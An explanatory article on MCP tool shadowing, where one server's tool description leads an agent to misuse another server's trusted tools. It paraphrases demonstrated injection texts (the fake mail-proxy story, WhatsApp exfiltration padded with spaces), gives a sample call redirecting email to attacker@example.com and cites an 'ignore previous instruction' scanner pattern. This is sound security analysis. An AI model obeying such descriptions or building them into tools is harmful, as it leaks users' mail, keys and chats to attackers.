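# Tool shadowing: how one MCP server's tool descriptions can change an agent's use of another server's tools

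## What is tool shadowing, and why can one server influence another's tools?

Tool shadowing is an attack on AI agents in which one tool provider puts instructions in its own tool's description that cause the agent to misuse a different, trusted provider's tool. The attacker needs no access to the trusted provider and no flaw in its code, because the agent reads both providers' descriptions together before it acts.

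Here, an agent is a language model that carries out tasks by calling tools, together with the software that runs it. A language model on its own only produces text, so it needs another program to send an email or query a database. A common way to connect the two is the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic introduced in November 2024. Anyone can publish a program that provides tools through MCP, and adoption was quick. In the summer of 2025, Li and Gao collected 67,057 of these programs, including some duplicates, from six public registries for *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol* (2025).

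### How a request travels through MCP

The application the user works in is the host. Cursor, a code editor, is one; Anthropic's Claude Desktop is another. A server is a program that offers tools to the host, and it may run on the user's own machine or on somebody else's. Behind the host stands the model, which reads text and decides which tool to use. (The host keeps one connector per server, the "client" in MCP's vocabulary, and some authors use that word for the whole host.)

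Suppose a user has connected two servers, one that sends email and one that does arithmetic. The host first sends each server a `tools/list` message to find out which tools it offers. Each server responds with a list of tool definitions, as specified in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026). A definition contains a name, a description in ordinary language, and a schema for the arguments the tool accepts. Whoever runs the server writes the description, which is free text.

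The host then merges the answers. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview* includes sample code for this step: the program starts with an empty list, goes through the servers one at a time, appends each server's tools, and registers the result with the conversation. For the user above, a simplified version of what reaches the model might look like this:

```
mail.send_email(to, subject, body)
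    Sends an email from the user's account.

calculator.add(a, b)
    Adds two numbers. [whatever else the calculator's author wrote]
```

Now the user asks the agent to email a colleague. The host sends the model a system prompt (the host's standing instructions), the merged tool list, and the conversation so far, including the new request. Together these make up the context, which is all the text the model reads before it acts. The model compares the request with the tool descriptions, picks `send_email`, and fills in the recipient, subject and body from what the user wrote. The model cannot send the email itself, so it returns the tool's name and arguments to the host, which sends a `tools/call` message to the mail server. The host adds the server's reply to the context, and the model tells the user that the email was sent.

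The specification recommends that a human always be able to refuse a tool call. The four hosts that Li and Gao examined (Cursor, Windsurf, Cline and Claude Desktop) asked for confirmation by default but also had an auto-run mode that skips confirmation.

The protocol has changed since then, although tool descriptions still enter the agent's context. The revision of 28 July 2026 removed sessions, and according to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), a server's tool list no longer varies between connections. A reviewer who inspects an honest server therefore sees the same list as other users with the same permissions, but a dishonest operator can ignore the rule.

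### Where the separation breaks down

Model Context Protocol (MCP) servers are designed to be isolated from one another. Each runs as its own program, with its own connection to the host. Under the principles on the protocol's architecture page, a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or "see into" other servers, and the host is responsible for enforcing that boundary.

This principle doesn't prevent shadowing, because it limits what a server can read, and shadowing depends on what a server can write. The arithmetic server in the example receives neither the mail server's tool list nor the user's conversation, but its description appears a few lines away from `send_email`, and the model reads both before it chooses a tool. In Li and Gao's threat model, the attacker controls only the text attached to its own tools, not the host, the other servers or the model. The attacker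 therefore has to guess which other tools are present, which is probably not hard, since registries publish what popular servers offer and a name like `send_email` is an obvious guess.

MCP does little to prevent tool shadowing. It does not dictate how applications manage the context they collect. Its safety principles say hosts should treat descriptions of tool behaviour as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, but the same document acknowledges that the protocol cannot enforce this. In practice, many hosts pass the descriptions on unchecked. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026) lists the host's connector storing descriptions without validating them as one step of a typical attack. Hosts also do little to check what the model returns. Among Li and Gao's four hosts, only Claude Desktop validated the arguments that the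 model returned, and it sometimes displayed a refusal and made the call anyway.

That leaves the model to tell honest text from dishonest text, which it can't do reliably. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026), a catalogue of 38 threats to MCP systems, traces the problem to how models follow instructions: when a model is choosing a tool, it can give text in a tool's description as much weight as a system-level instruction.

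Malicious instructions are especially hard to recognize in tool descriptions because honest descriptions contain instructions too. Li and Gao found a real email server on the registry mcp.so whose description for listing messages has a block marked "Important". The block tells the model to use a second tool, `mark_email_as_handled`, to clear a message from the inbox. They treated this as an unintended risk, not an attack, but it has the same form as a shadowing attack, because text attached to one tool governs the use of another. The difference is whose interest the instruction serves, and a model cannot tell that from the wording.

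Recognizing malicious instructions as abnormal may not stop a model from following them either. In Li and Gao's tests of malicious descriptions and error messages, Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro could identify the planted instructions as abnormal in its displayed reasoning, but it still followed them. Its stated reason was that it was preferable to proceed.

### Tool poisoning, and how shadowing differs

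Prompt injection is an attack that places instructions in text a model reads, such as a web page, an email or a file, so that the model obeys someone other than the user. Tool poisoning is prompt injection placed in a tool's description or other metadata. The term comes from *MCP Security Notification*, which Luca Beurer-Kellner and Marc Fischer of Invariant Labs published on 1 April 2025. Invariant Labs builds security software for agents.

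Their first example is a tool called `add`, which takes two numbers and a third argument, `sidenote`, that addition does not need. Its description begins with the tool's stated purpose, adding two numbers. A block tagged as important then contains instructions for the model to read two files and pass their contents as the `sidenote`. One is Cursor's configuration file, which often holds credentials for other servers. The other is the user's private SSH key, which can let its holder log in to the user's other machines. The model is also told to explain the mathematics of addition to the user in detail while it does this, and not to mention the file access.

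Li and Gao used a version of the same tool and described the attack step by step. When the user asks for a sum, the model first requests the host's own file-reading tool, the host runs it, and the key's contents enter the context. The model then calls `add` with the two numbers and the key as arguments, which sends the key to the attacker's server. When Invariant Labs ran the attack, Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but the dialog did not show the full arguments, even in its extended view, so the user could not see the key.

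The description is the most obvious place to hide such text, but Shen and colleagues also cover schema poisoning, since a schema's argument names, default values and titles all reach the model. They cite researchers at the security firm CyberArk, who added an extra field to a tool's schema and got a model to follow the instruction inside it.

Tool shadowing is a form of tool poisoning in which one server's tool description changes how the agent uses another server's tool. In the `add` example, the key leaves the machine only if the agent calls `add`, so a user who never needs a sum loses nothing, and a user who inspects the full call might catch the theft. Shadowing removes both limits because the malicious tool need never run. Invariant Labs' second experiment used another bogus `add` tool. Its description diverted emails the user sent through a trusted server, and the agent did not have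 to call `add` for this to work.

(*Securing the AI Agent* (2026) names tool poisoning, tool shadowing and rug pulls side by side, as if they were three separate attacks. Since a shadowing description is a poisoned description, it is simpler to treat shadowing as one kind of poisoning.)

The security firm Trail of Bits uses the name "line jumping" for attacks that take effect before any tool runs. Its *Jumping the line* explains why two of MCP's protections, user consent and server isolation, miss them. The host asks the user for consent before it calls a tool, but a tool's description enters the context as soon as the host connects to the server, when there is no call to approve. Isolation leaves the servers with no direct channel between them, but the model still carries the malicious server's instructions into its interactions with the trusted server.

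The harmful action in a shadowing attack looks like an ordinary call to a legitimate tool, made with the user's own permissions. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), a formal study of attacks on agents, shows that revoking only the server that supplied a suspicious description does not stop shadowing, because the injected call goes to the trusted server.

A rug pull is a change to a tool's description or behaviour after the user has approved the tool. MCP allows tool lists to change, so a server can pass an initial review with a harmless description and add the shadowing text later.

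### Other meanings of "shadowing"

Authors use the term "tool shadowing" differently, so a success rate reported for it may measure something else. Invariant Labs uses it in the sense above, influence through a description, as do Li and Gao and *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*.

In *MCP-DPT* (2026), a taxonomy of MCP attacks and of the places to defend against them, tool shadowing instead means that a malicious tool or server closely imitates the name and description of a trusted one. The agent then calls the malicious tool, whereas in Invariant's attack it calls the trusted tool but uses it incorrectly. *MCPSECBENCH* (Yang, Gao and colleagues, 2026), a benchmark of 17 attacks, uses the term for a third arrangement. Its test prompt directs the model to a legitimate verification tool and then straight on to a second tool, which alters the verified output. Shen and colleagues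 try to keep the meanings apart, with separate entries for name spoofing (MCP-13) and cross-server influence through the context (MCP-14), but their summary table describes MCP-14 as a name conflict too. They also list "shadow MCP servers", which are servers that someone runs inside an organisation without its approval.

The newest use of the term is even further from tool shadowing. *ShadowBench-MCP* (Al-Masri and Yang, 2026) studies "shadow invocations", in which a harmless-sounding change in the user's request leads the model to use a riskier series of tools. For example, the user might ask for the same software patch but want it done the fastest way, or with the audit postponed. The study tested one model, Qwen3-32B, on six kinds of security-sensitive work. The changed wording produced a riskier route in 14 of 48 comparisons when the model's instructions favoured efficiency, compared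 with 2 of 48 when they made the relevant safety checks mandatory. Nobody alters a tool description and no server is malicious, so the result has no direct bearing on tool shadowing.

Identical tool names can cause one server's tool to run in place of another's, even without misleading text. Under MCP, tool names should be unique within a server but can repeat across servers, so two servers may each offer a `send_email` tool. The specification recommends that hosts tell them apart, for instance with a prefix for each server, and Cursor added such prefixes. Li and Gao connected two servers with identically named email tools and asked for a message to be sent. The log shows that the model chose the second server's tool, but the reply came from the first server because Cursor ignored the prefixes when it made the call. Whichever tool the model picked, Cursor ran the one whose server came first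 in the user's configuration file. Cursor acknowledged the behaviour and classified it as a functional issue.

That fault is in the host's code, and a programmer can fix it by making the host respect the prefix. The fix would not prevent shadowing, because in a shadowing attack the host calls the tool the model selected, on the correct server, with arguments the attacker has already influenced.

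## What did the demonstrations show?

In the first week of April 2025, Invariant Labs demonstrated tool shadowing twice in Cursor. In the first, the agent sent a user's emails to an attacker, and in the second, it leaked the user's WhatsApp messages.

### The redirected email

In the shadowing experiment from Invariant Labs' 1 April disclosure, Beurer-Kellner and Fischer connected Cursor to a trusted server with a `send_email` tool and a malicious server with a bogus tool for adding numbers, called `add`. The bogus tool was much like the one they had used to steal an SSH key.

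The description of `add` began with the tool's supposed purpose, followed by a made-up technical problem. According to the description, while this tool was available, all email had to go to one particular address to prevent "proxying issues", and the real recipient would be extracted from the body of the message. Putting the real recipient in the recipient field would supposedly crash the application and lose all data. The description also included an instruction not to mention this to the user, because it was only an implementation detail and the user deserved the best experience.

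This text contains no request to harm the user, and if its story were true, redirecting the email would be helpful. The attack may not need this much persuasion. Li and Gao later reproduced it with a description that just gave the attacker's address as the "actual recipient" for `send_email`.

Suppose the user asks Cursor to send Anna a report. The model correctly chooses `send_email`, but it fills in the arguments as the malicious description directs. In simplified form:

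```
The call the user expects:
send_email(to="anna@example.com", subject="Report",
           body="Here is the report.")

The call the model writes:
send_email(to="attacker@example.com", subject="Report",
           body="Recipient: anna@example.com. Here is the report.")
```

The confirmation dialog, which had hidden the SSH key in the earlier experiment, shows the tool name the user expects, so the user has little reason to look further. Once the user approves the call, the mail server executes it as specified and the attacker receives the report.

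The altered address appeared only in the call's arguments, and the agent did not mention a different recipient anywhere else in the log. A user who expanded the call and read the address could have caught the change. But Li and Gao found that Cursor, Windsurf and Claude Desktop all showed short summaries by default, so a user would see only a confirmation that the email had been sent.

The "proxy" does not exist, so Anna receives nothing unless the attacker forwards the message, and she may eventually ask where her report is. Shen and colleagues list a variant that is harder for her to notice, in which the planted text makes the agent add a `bcc` (blind copy) recipient. Anna gets her email as usual and cannot see that somebody else got it too.

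Beurer-Kellner and Fischer summed up the result as "Shadowing Is Enough". The agent never has to call `add` for the attack to work, so the log shows only calls to trusted tools. An investigator would find a wrong address in a call to the mail server but nothing that points to `add`. They would have to read the descriptions of every connected tool to find the cause, and by then the attacker might have restored a harmless description.

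### The WhatsApp demonstration

The second demonstration targeted whatsapp-mcp, a real, public server that lets an agent search and send WhatsApp messages. A developer had released it only a week earlier. lharries explained in the launch post, *WhatsApp MCP Server* (2025), that it stores all messages in a database on the user's machine and sends nothing to the cloud unless the user lets the model read the messages through its tools. Beurer-Kellner replied to the post with a warning about MCP's security risks.

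Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (7 April 2025) combined shadowing with a rug pull. On the first launch, the malicious server described its tool `get_fact_of_the_day` in one harmless line about getting a random fact, and the user approved it. On the second launch, the server supplied a different description. Some hosts showed users a tool's description at installation but did not notify them when it changed, so the new text reached the model without a new approval. An attacker could also switch the description only for certain users or for a short time, making the attack harder to trace.

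The new description used another story about a proxy. It instructed the agent, whenever it called WhatsApp's `send_message` tool, to replace the recipient with the attacker's phone number and put the real recipient in the message body. The agent was also told to attach the results of any earlier `list_chats` call, supposedly so that the proxy could verify the user's identity. The description specified the exact message format, including a long run of spaces between the user's words and the stolen data.

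Because of those spaces, a user could read everything visible in the confirmation dialog and still approve the theft. Cursor displayed the recipient and the message this time, but the recipient was a bare phone number, which few people would check against their contacts, and the message seemed to contain only "Hi". The stolen data was far off to the right, and Cursor hid the scrollbar that would have suggested there was more text.

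WhatsApp's encryption did not prevent the attack, because it protects a message on its way to the recipient, and here the recipient was the attacker. Running the malicious server in a sandbox would not have helped either, since the attack used only the server's tool description.

Invariant Labs reported that the attack could leak a user's entire chat history "when in context". The planted instructions relied on what `list_chats` had already returned, so messages the agent had not loaded were not at risk from this particular text.

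A second experiment, added on 9 April, did not require a malicious server. The attacker sent the user a WhatsApp message containing similar instructions, and the agent leaked the user's contacts after reading it.

### How strong the evidence is

These demonstrations show that the attacks are possible, but they are weak evidence of how often the attacks would work on somebody else's machine. Neither write-up states how many attempts the researchers made, how many failed, or which model Cursor was using.

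The researchers also knew the set-up they were attacking. Their first description used the exact label `mcp_tool_send_email`, which a real attacker would have had to guess. The WhatsApp demonstration is more realistic in this respect, because anyone could look up a public server's tool names. Some of the disclosure's warnings also went further than its experiments. For example, it described how a malicious server might cause credentials from one server to be secretly passed to another, but its shadowing experiment only redirected email.

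Invariant Labs had a commercial interest in the problem. Both posts promoted its security products, and SiliconANGLE's *Snyk acquires Invariant Labs to expand AI agent security capabilities* (2025) reported in June that the security company Snyk had bought it. This is a reason to be careful with Invariant Labs' description of the flaw as "critical", but a weaker reason to doubt the experiments, because outsiders could run them. Invariant Labs released the code for both attacks in *MCP Tool Poisoning Experiments* (2025), a public repository created on 6 April.

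Trail of Bits reported the same effect on 21 April with a very different tool description. It described an invented operating system, Kpyndzkyff, as almost identical to Linux except that every command needed a certain prefix. The prefix was a real command that lets every account on the machine read and write the files in the user's home directory. The description also listed questions, such as how much disk space was left, for which the model should follow these instructions without calling the malicious tool. The hosts and models that Trail of Bits tested, including Claude Desktop, added the prefix when they used other servers' tools. Trail of Bits gave no trial counts either, but its result makes it unlikely that the effect depended on email, on Cursor or on Invariant's wording.

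### Would anyone install such a server?

One objection is that the victim has to connect a malicious server first. Programmers argued about this on the forum Hacker News in April 2025, in a discussion of *The “S” in MCP Stands for Security*, an article that drew on Invariant's disclosure. One commenter asked why anybody would use an untrusted tool, and why people who did were surprised to be vulnerable.

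Beurer-Kellner had pointed out in the same discussion that a server can change its tools at any time, or for one specific user, and that Claude and Cursor did not notify users of such changes. Even a careful user can therefore install a harmless server that later becomes malicious. Someone other than the original developer could also make the switch. Li and Gao found 304 servers in public registries whose links relied on a GitHub account name that the owner had given up. GitHub redirected visitors to the new address, but anybody could register the old name and publish a different server under it.

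This answers the objection as long as hosts accept changed descriptions without warning users. It also shows that the April attacks depended partly on the host makers' choice not to give that warning.

Another commenter thought the attack was redundant because a server on the user's own machine already runs with the user's permissions and can read the SSH keys without tricking a model. This is largely right for local servers, and it also applies to the WhatsApp demonstration. The whatsapp-mcp server keeps its messages in a local database, so a malicious program running on the same machine with the same permissions could have copied them directly.

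Shadowing is much more useful to an attacker when the malicious server is remote or confined to a sandbox. A remote weather service cannot open the user's files or send email from the user's account, but the agent that reads the service's tool description can do both. Other commenters replied that the user has given the agent access to private data and may not realize that the weather company can now influence what the agent does with it.

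### A new flaw or an old one?

Invariant Labs described its discovery as a vulnerability in MCP. The software developer Simon Willison took the demonstrations seriously but argued in *Model Context Protocol has prompt injection security problems* (2025) that the problems were "not inherent to the MCP protocol itself". In his view, they arise whenever a model has tools and might read untrusted text, and developers had known about prompt injection for more than two and a half years without finding a convincing remedy.

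ChatGPT plugins, a predecessor of MCP servers, showed in 2023 that a tool's description alone could influence a conversation. *LLM Platform Security* (2023), a study of those plugins, describes AMZPRO, which helped people write product listings for Amazon. Its description told ChatGPT to always reply in English. When the researchers enabled AMZPRO but did not use it, ChatGPT answered in English for the rest of the session, even when the question was in another language. AMZPRO wasn't malicious, and it changed the conversation, not another plugin's behaviour.

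Wu, Roesner and colleagues demonstrated a closer precedent in *IsolateGPT* (2024), a year before Invariant's disclosure. They built two ride-hailing apps for a test system based on GPT-4 and asked it to find the cheaper ride. The malicious app, Quick Ride, contained instructions to add $10 to every fare from its competitor, Metro Hail, and the model did so. This was essentially tool shadowing, though the paper didn't call it that, and the model altered the fares Metro Hail reported rather than the arguments sent to it.

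The problem also exists in newer products outside MCP. *MCP*, an analysis on the security blog Embrace The Red, includes a demonstration with ChatGPT's AI Actions, which connect to outside services through the OpenAPI standard. A short message in the interface description was enough to control ChatGPT's response.

Beurer-Kellner did not really dispute this. On Hacker News he called tool shadowing a special form of prompt injection. The remaining disagreement is mostly about how much MCP adds. It adds at least two things: it lets a host discover tools while running, which made the WhatsApp rug pull so easy, and it encourages users to combine servers from unrelated developers. A tool description may also be a better place to hide malicious instructions than ordinary data. Invariant found it slightly harder to make the injected WhatsApp message work than the poisoned description, possibly because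 developers train models to give tool outputs less authority.

Willison described agents as vulnerable to "confused deputy" attacks, in which someone tricks a program into misusing its authority. The term comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 account of an incident at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. Tymshare's compiler had permission to write to a system directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The compiler overwrote the billing records, even though the user had no permission to write to that file.

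In Invariant's email attack, the agent is the confused deputy. The malicious server cannot send email from the user's account, but it can supply an address, and the agent then sends email to that address with the user's authority. The mail server cannot detect that the address came from the malicious server rather than the user.

The known solution to Hardy's problem is to require whoever names a file to also supply the permission to use it. The compiler would then have had no right to write its debugging output to the billing file. This is harder to arrange for an agent, because names and instructions arrive mixed in ordinary prose. One commenter on Hacker News wanted models to have an ironclad distinction between the user's instructions and outside text that they must not obey. Beurer-Kellner doubted that this was compatible with what people expect of agents, since an agent asked to install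 a software library has to read the library's documentation and follow the instructions in it. The commenter replied that the agent should treat those instructions as information about how to reach the user's goal, and judge whether each step serves that goal. But to judge correctly in the email attack, the model would have had to recognize that the proxy story was false.

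## How often does it succeed, and has it been used in real attacks?

Published success rates for tool shadowing and closely related attacks range from below 1% to 100%, depending on the model, the attack and how the researchers defined success. Real attackers have poisoned tool descriptions and stolen email through an MCP server, but none of the cases described below is confirmed as tool shadowing.

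### The email attack in four hosts

Li and Gao repeated Invariant's email redirection in Cursor, Windsurf, Cline and Claude Desktop. They used GPT-4o, Claude Sonnet 4 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, except in Claude Desktop, which offered only Sonnet 4. They ran the test five times for each of the ten pairs of host and model.

The attack worked in most settings in Cursor, Windsurf and Cline, and the only reported failure was with GPT-4o in Windsurf. Claude Desktop sometimes blocked the call, but it could also display a refusal and make the call anyway. That is arguably worse than having no check, because the user would assume the email had not been sent.

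Li and Gao intended only to show that the attack is feasible. Five runs are enough for that, but too few to show how often it works. If the true success rate were only 55%, all five runs would still succeed about 5% of the time.

In their separate tests of tool poisoning, success may have depended on the host as well as the model. A description that directed GPT-4o to misuse the host's own tools worked in four runs out of five in Cursor, two in Cline and one in Windsurf. With so few runs, though, chance could explain the difference.

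### A larger test on 2025 models

Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025) tested many more cases in *MCPTox*. With help from language models, they wrote poisoned tools to accompany 353 tools from 45 real servers. In each test, the model received an ordinary request, with one poisoned tool listed alongside a server's real ones. The attack succeeded if the model responded by calling a legitimate tool to carry out the attacker's instruction. Calling the poisoned tool itself counted as a failure, so the benchmark measures something close to tool shadowing.

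The attack success rate is the share of valid test runs in which the agent did what the attacker wanted. It averaged 36.5% across 20 model settings (some models ran both with and without step-by-step reasoning) and was highest for OpenAI's o1-mini, at 72.8%.

The email redirection is an example of what Wang and colleagues call parameter tampering, in which the poisoned description changes an argument in a call the user wanted. This class had the highest average success rate, at 46.7%. The other two classes, which made the agent take an extra action such as reading an SSH key, averaged 36.7% and 26.7%. Wang and colleagues suggest that tampering is harder for a model to detect because the call still matches the user's request. Depending on the wording, tampering succeeded 83% to 90% of the time against o1-mini and 6% to 54% of the time against Claude 3.7 Sonnet.

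The most successful descriptions combined a condition that triggers the action, the action itself, and a plausible reason for it. Invariant's story about a mail proxy has all three. Wang and colleagues also tested attack texts from an older benchmark, InjecAgent, but these contained only the malicious action, and almost none worked as tool descriptions. Against the small model Qwen3-8b with reasoning switched on, they succeeded 0.1% of the time, compared with 41.8% for the purpose-built descriptions.

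More forceful wording helped much less. An "important" tag raised the average success rate by 2.0 percentage points, and telling the model to ignore all previous instructions raised it by 2.6. With Claude 3.7 Sonnet, however, the tag cut the success rate of parameter tampering from 47.7% to 6.4%, possibly because it made the text look more suspicious.

Most attacks failed because the model ignored the poisoned description rather than because it detected the attack. Claude 3.7 Sonnet refused most often, but in fewer than 3% of cases. In 18.9% of failures, the model called the poisoned tool.

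The benchmark scored the calls that models wrote but did not execute them. This matters fairly little for a redirected email, because hosts generally run a call with whatever arguments the model returns, although a user could still refuse it. The test favored the attacker more by giving the language models that helped write the poisoned descriptions the complete tool list of the server under attack. The paper's abstract gives 1,348 test cases, but the three classes in its table add up to 1,497.

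### Attacks with real tool calls

In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) let their agents' tool calls run. They built agents with 11 frameworks (software libraries for building agents, such as LangChain) and, in a twelfth set-up, with OpenAI's programming interface and no framework. Over three days in July 2026, they tried 45 attack scenarios on 18 models in each set-up, 9,720 combinations in all.

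Each agent connected to a malicious server and an honest one with tools for handling files and making web requests, then received a harmless task. The researchers planted a secret in a file in the agent's workspace and ran a web server that stood in for the attacker's. The attack counted as successful if the web server received a request, if the agent made a call containing the web server's address or the secret, or if the agent read the file containing the secret.

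By this measure, attacks succeeded in 2,113 of 9,215 valid runs, or 22.9%. Repeating the whole experiment changed the rate by only 0.1 percentage points.

The secret reached the researchers' web server in 255 runs, about 2.8% of the valid ones. In another 487 runs, the agent contacted that server without sending the secret. Most of the remaining successes (1,067) were calls to the malicious MCP server's own tools, which recorded the call and returned a dummy answer. A real attacker would have received anything the agent put in those calls, so 2.8% probably understates the danger.

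Reported success rates can also be too high. Ahmed and Abbas (2026), in *Labels Are Not Endpoints*, re-examined their own MCP experiment and found that their grading program could record a successful attack only when the tool information was poisoned, so properly completing a two-step task counted as a pass in the clean condition and as a hijacking in the poisoned one. They reclassified 58 supposed attacks as ordinary completed tasks, which left three real transfers of protected data and one case of unauthorized forwarding.

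Shaikh and Montaruli's test is less prone to this error, because an agent is unlikely to contact the attacker's address by accident. But in 290 of the runs they counted as successes, the agent only read the planted file. Shaikh and Montaruli did not run the same tasks without an attack, so some of those agents might have read the file anyway.

None of their figures measures how often tool shadowing succeeds. In about half of the successes, the agent called the attacker's own tool, whereas shadowing works through a trusted one. Fourteen of the scenarios gave the malicious tool the same name as a legitimate tool, so they also involve name conflicts, which are a separate problem. One attack class, called "semantic shadowing", succeeded in 13.9% of runs (29 of 208), but it consists of a single scenario, which tests whether the model believes a claim in the description without running the mechanism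 the claim refers to.

Their "cross-tool reference" attack is closer to Invariant's. The description tells the agent to use a named legitimate tool to send a file of secrets to the attacker before responding to the user. Shaikh and Montaruli list this among their three most successful designs, but their results by attack class don't list it separately. The rates they do give range from 51.9% for "parameter binding", a form of argument injection, to zero for instructions hidden in invisible characters.

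The choice of framework made little difference on average. Nine of the twelve set-ups, including the one without a framework, had success rates between 23.4% and 26.1%. The exceptions had technical causes:

- AG2 (4.6%) rarely completed the outgoing calls that the attacks needed.
- Pydantic AI (16.6%) refused to register two tools with the same name.
- smolagents (34.4%) presented tools to the model as Python code, which seems to have made the attacks easier.

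For some models, the differences were larger than these averages show. With Llama 4 Maverick, the success rate varied by 36.5 percentage points across the nine similar set-ups.

The choice of model mattered much more, as this selection from Shaikh and Montaruli's results shows:

| Model | Successful attacks / valid runs | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 2 / 465 | 0.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 8 / 530 | 1.5% |
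| Claude Sonnet 5 | 10 / 527 | 1.9% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 19 / 534 | 3.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 44 / 354 | 12.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 77 / 530 | 14.5% |
| Mistral Large 3 | 233 / 533 | 43.7% |
| Amazon Nova Pro | 245 / 493 | 49.7% |

### Are more capable models easier to fool?

Wang and colleagues concluded in 2025 that more capable models were often more susceptible because they were better at following instructions, including the attacker's. Their evidence is stronger for the effect of reasoning than for the effect of model size. Turning on reasoning raised the success rate against Qwen3-32b from 23.7% to 58.5%, and the other Qwen3 models showed the same pattern. But attacks succeeded less often against the 14-billion-parameter Qwen3 than against the 8-billion one, and less often against the 235-billion version than against the 32-billion one.

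The newest Claude models in the 2026 test do not fit the 2025 conclusion. They are much more capable than o1-mini, yet the attacks on them almost always failed. Opus 4.8 explicitly refused in 223 of 530 runs (about 42%), citing the poisoned description, so its low attack success rate came at least partly from recognizing the attacks.

Other developers' models did not all improve. Attacks succeeded twice as often against Mistral Large 3 as against its predecessor. Claude Sonnet 5 identified the prompt injection in four of its ten failures but still made the harmful call.

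A model that seldom completes tool calls can have a low attack success rate even if its judgement is poor. This may help explain why attacks on DeepSeek-R1 succeeded 70.9% of the time in MCPTox but 3.6% of the time in Shaikh and Montaruli's later test. Shaikh and Montaruli did not measure how well the models did their tasks without an attack, so it is unclear how often R1 failed to complete tool calls. The attacks and set-ups also differed, and the researchers may have used different versions of the model. Failed tool calls are a less likely explanation for Opus 4.8's low rate, given its many explicit refusals.

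The low Claude rates also come from a fixed set of attacks. Every model faced the same 45 scenarios, which drew on published techniques, and Shaikh and Montaruli acknowledge that some models may have seen similar attacks in training. A real attacker could keep rewriting a description until it worked. Shaikh and Montaruli cite MCP-ITP, an automated system for generating poisoned descriptions, which had an 84.2% success rate with tools that the agent never called. It is unclear whether Fable 5's rate would stay at 0.4% against that kind of search.

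### Suspicious descriptions in public registries

Li and Gao also looked for malicious descriptions in the servers they had collected from four public registries in the summer of 2025. Their scanner, MCPInspect, searched for phrases such as "ignore previous instruction" and labels such as "important", and flagged 18 servers.

A manual check of the 18 showed that most were demonstrations. One, Damn Vulnerable MCP Server, is deliberately insecure so that people can learn from it. Five others contained carelessly written instructions for the model to use additional tools, such as the email server's instruction to use `mark_email_as_handled`. None of the 18 appears to have been a live attack.

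The search could easily have missed one. A shadowing description in plain language, without a conspicuous label, would have passed, and so would a server that sent its malicious text only after installation. Registries do not seem to have become much stricter since then. The Hacker News' *Welcome to the Jungle* (2026) reported in October that the security company OX had found no marketplace vetting across 15,465 listed servers, some of which pointed to expired domains. (The Hacker News is a security news site, not the forum Hacker News.)

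### Poisoned descriptions in real attacks

By early 2026, attackers were using poisoned tool descriptions in real malware. *SANDWORM_MODE* (Raj, 2026) describes a February attack that used malicious packages named to resemble popular ones on npm, a public collection of JavaScript software. The malware installed its own MCP server on the victim's machine and registered it with coding assistants such as Cursor. According to SC Media, the server offered three tools whose descriptions contained instructions for the assistant to collect SSH keys, cloud credentials and other secrets. This was tool poisoning, but the reported instructions targeted files and settings, not another server's tools.

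The "Deadbugz" campaign of August 2026 more closely resembled Invariant's WhatsApp demonstration. *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026), published by Pillar Security, describes a server called `productivity-suite` with two harmless-looking tools, one for formatting text and one for summarizing it. The server counted each client's tool calls and, after the third, replaced its tool descriptions with instructions to look for SSH keys, cloud credentials and command history, and to hide this from the user. A reviewer who made only one or two test calls would have seen nothing wrong, although the malicious text was in the server's public source code all along.

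The attacker tried to spread the server through pull requests, which are proposed changes to other people's software projects. On 10 August, one GitHub account submitted 23 pull requests in 74 minutes, most of which would have added the server to a project's MCP configuration. When Pillar reviewed them, the projects had closed 19 without merging and the other four were still open.

It is unclear whether Deadbugz involved tool shadowing. Fogel's report calls the malicious instructions "cross-tool" in two captions, but its text does not name any other server's tool that the instructions were meant to affect. Fogel confirmed that the live server sent the altered instructions but did not report any victims. On the published evidence, Deadbugz was an attempted tool-poisoning attack with a delayed trigger.

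### Theft without shadowing

The best-known theft of email through an MCP server relied on malicious code in the server, not on manipulating the model. A developer copied the official code for connecting agents to Postmark, an email service, and published it on npm as `postmark-mcp`. The security company Koi found that the first 15 versions worked normally. Version 1.0.16, which came out on 17 September 2025 according to The Hacker News (2025), added one line of code that sent a blind copy of every email to the developer's address. OSV's public malware record, *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), also identifies 1.0.16 as the first malicious version.

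For the user, the result was much like that of a shadowing attack that adds a `bcc` recipient. But in a shadowing attack the model writes the extra address into its call to a legitimate mail server, whereas the malicious `postmark-mcp` server added the address after the model had made a correct call. A model that followed the user's instructions perfectly, or recognized every prompt injection, would not have prevented this.

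The amount of email the developer stole is uncertain. Koi estimated 3,000 to 15,000 messages a day by guessing that 20% of the package's 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use and that each represented an organization sending 10 to 50 emails a day. The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi asked about it, but this did not remove the copies already on users' machines.

Attackers were still using ordinary malicious code in late 2026. ThreatRoundup's *Fake MCP Servers on GitHub Rob You* (2026) describes two servers that supposedly let an agent check a user's points on cryptocurrency exchanges. The servers installed password-stealing and clipboard-hijacking malware as soon as the host started them, before the agent had called any tool. The clipboard hijacker's wallets had received about $49,900 since February.

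These attackers had little reason to use tool shadowing, because their own code already ran on the victim's machine or handled the victim's email. The lack of confirmed cases is only weak evidence that nobody has tried tool shadowing. Anyone could find the extra line in `postmark-mcp` by reading the package, but a poisoned description on a remote server may be gone by the time anyone looks.

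## Which defences stop it, and who should apply them?

The most reliable way to stop tool shadowing is to keep an untrusted server's descriptions out of any conversation in which the agent uses sensitive tools. Pinning, scanning and confirmation dialogs are easier to add to existing hosts, but each stops only some versions of the attack. People also disagree about who should add them. Four organisations rejected reports from researchers who had found these protections missing.

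Invariant Labs proposed three defences in its April 2025 disclosure: show users the full tool descriptions, pin tools so they cannot change unnoticed, and put stricter boundaries between servers. The email redirection attack in the same disclosure is a good test of each.

### Pinning

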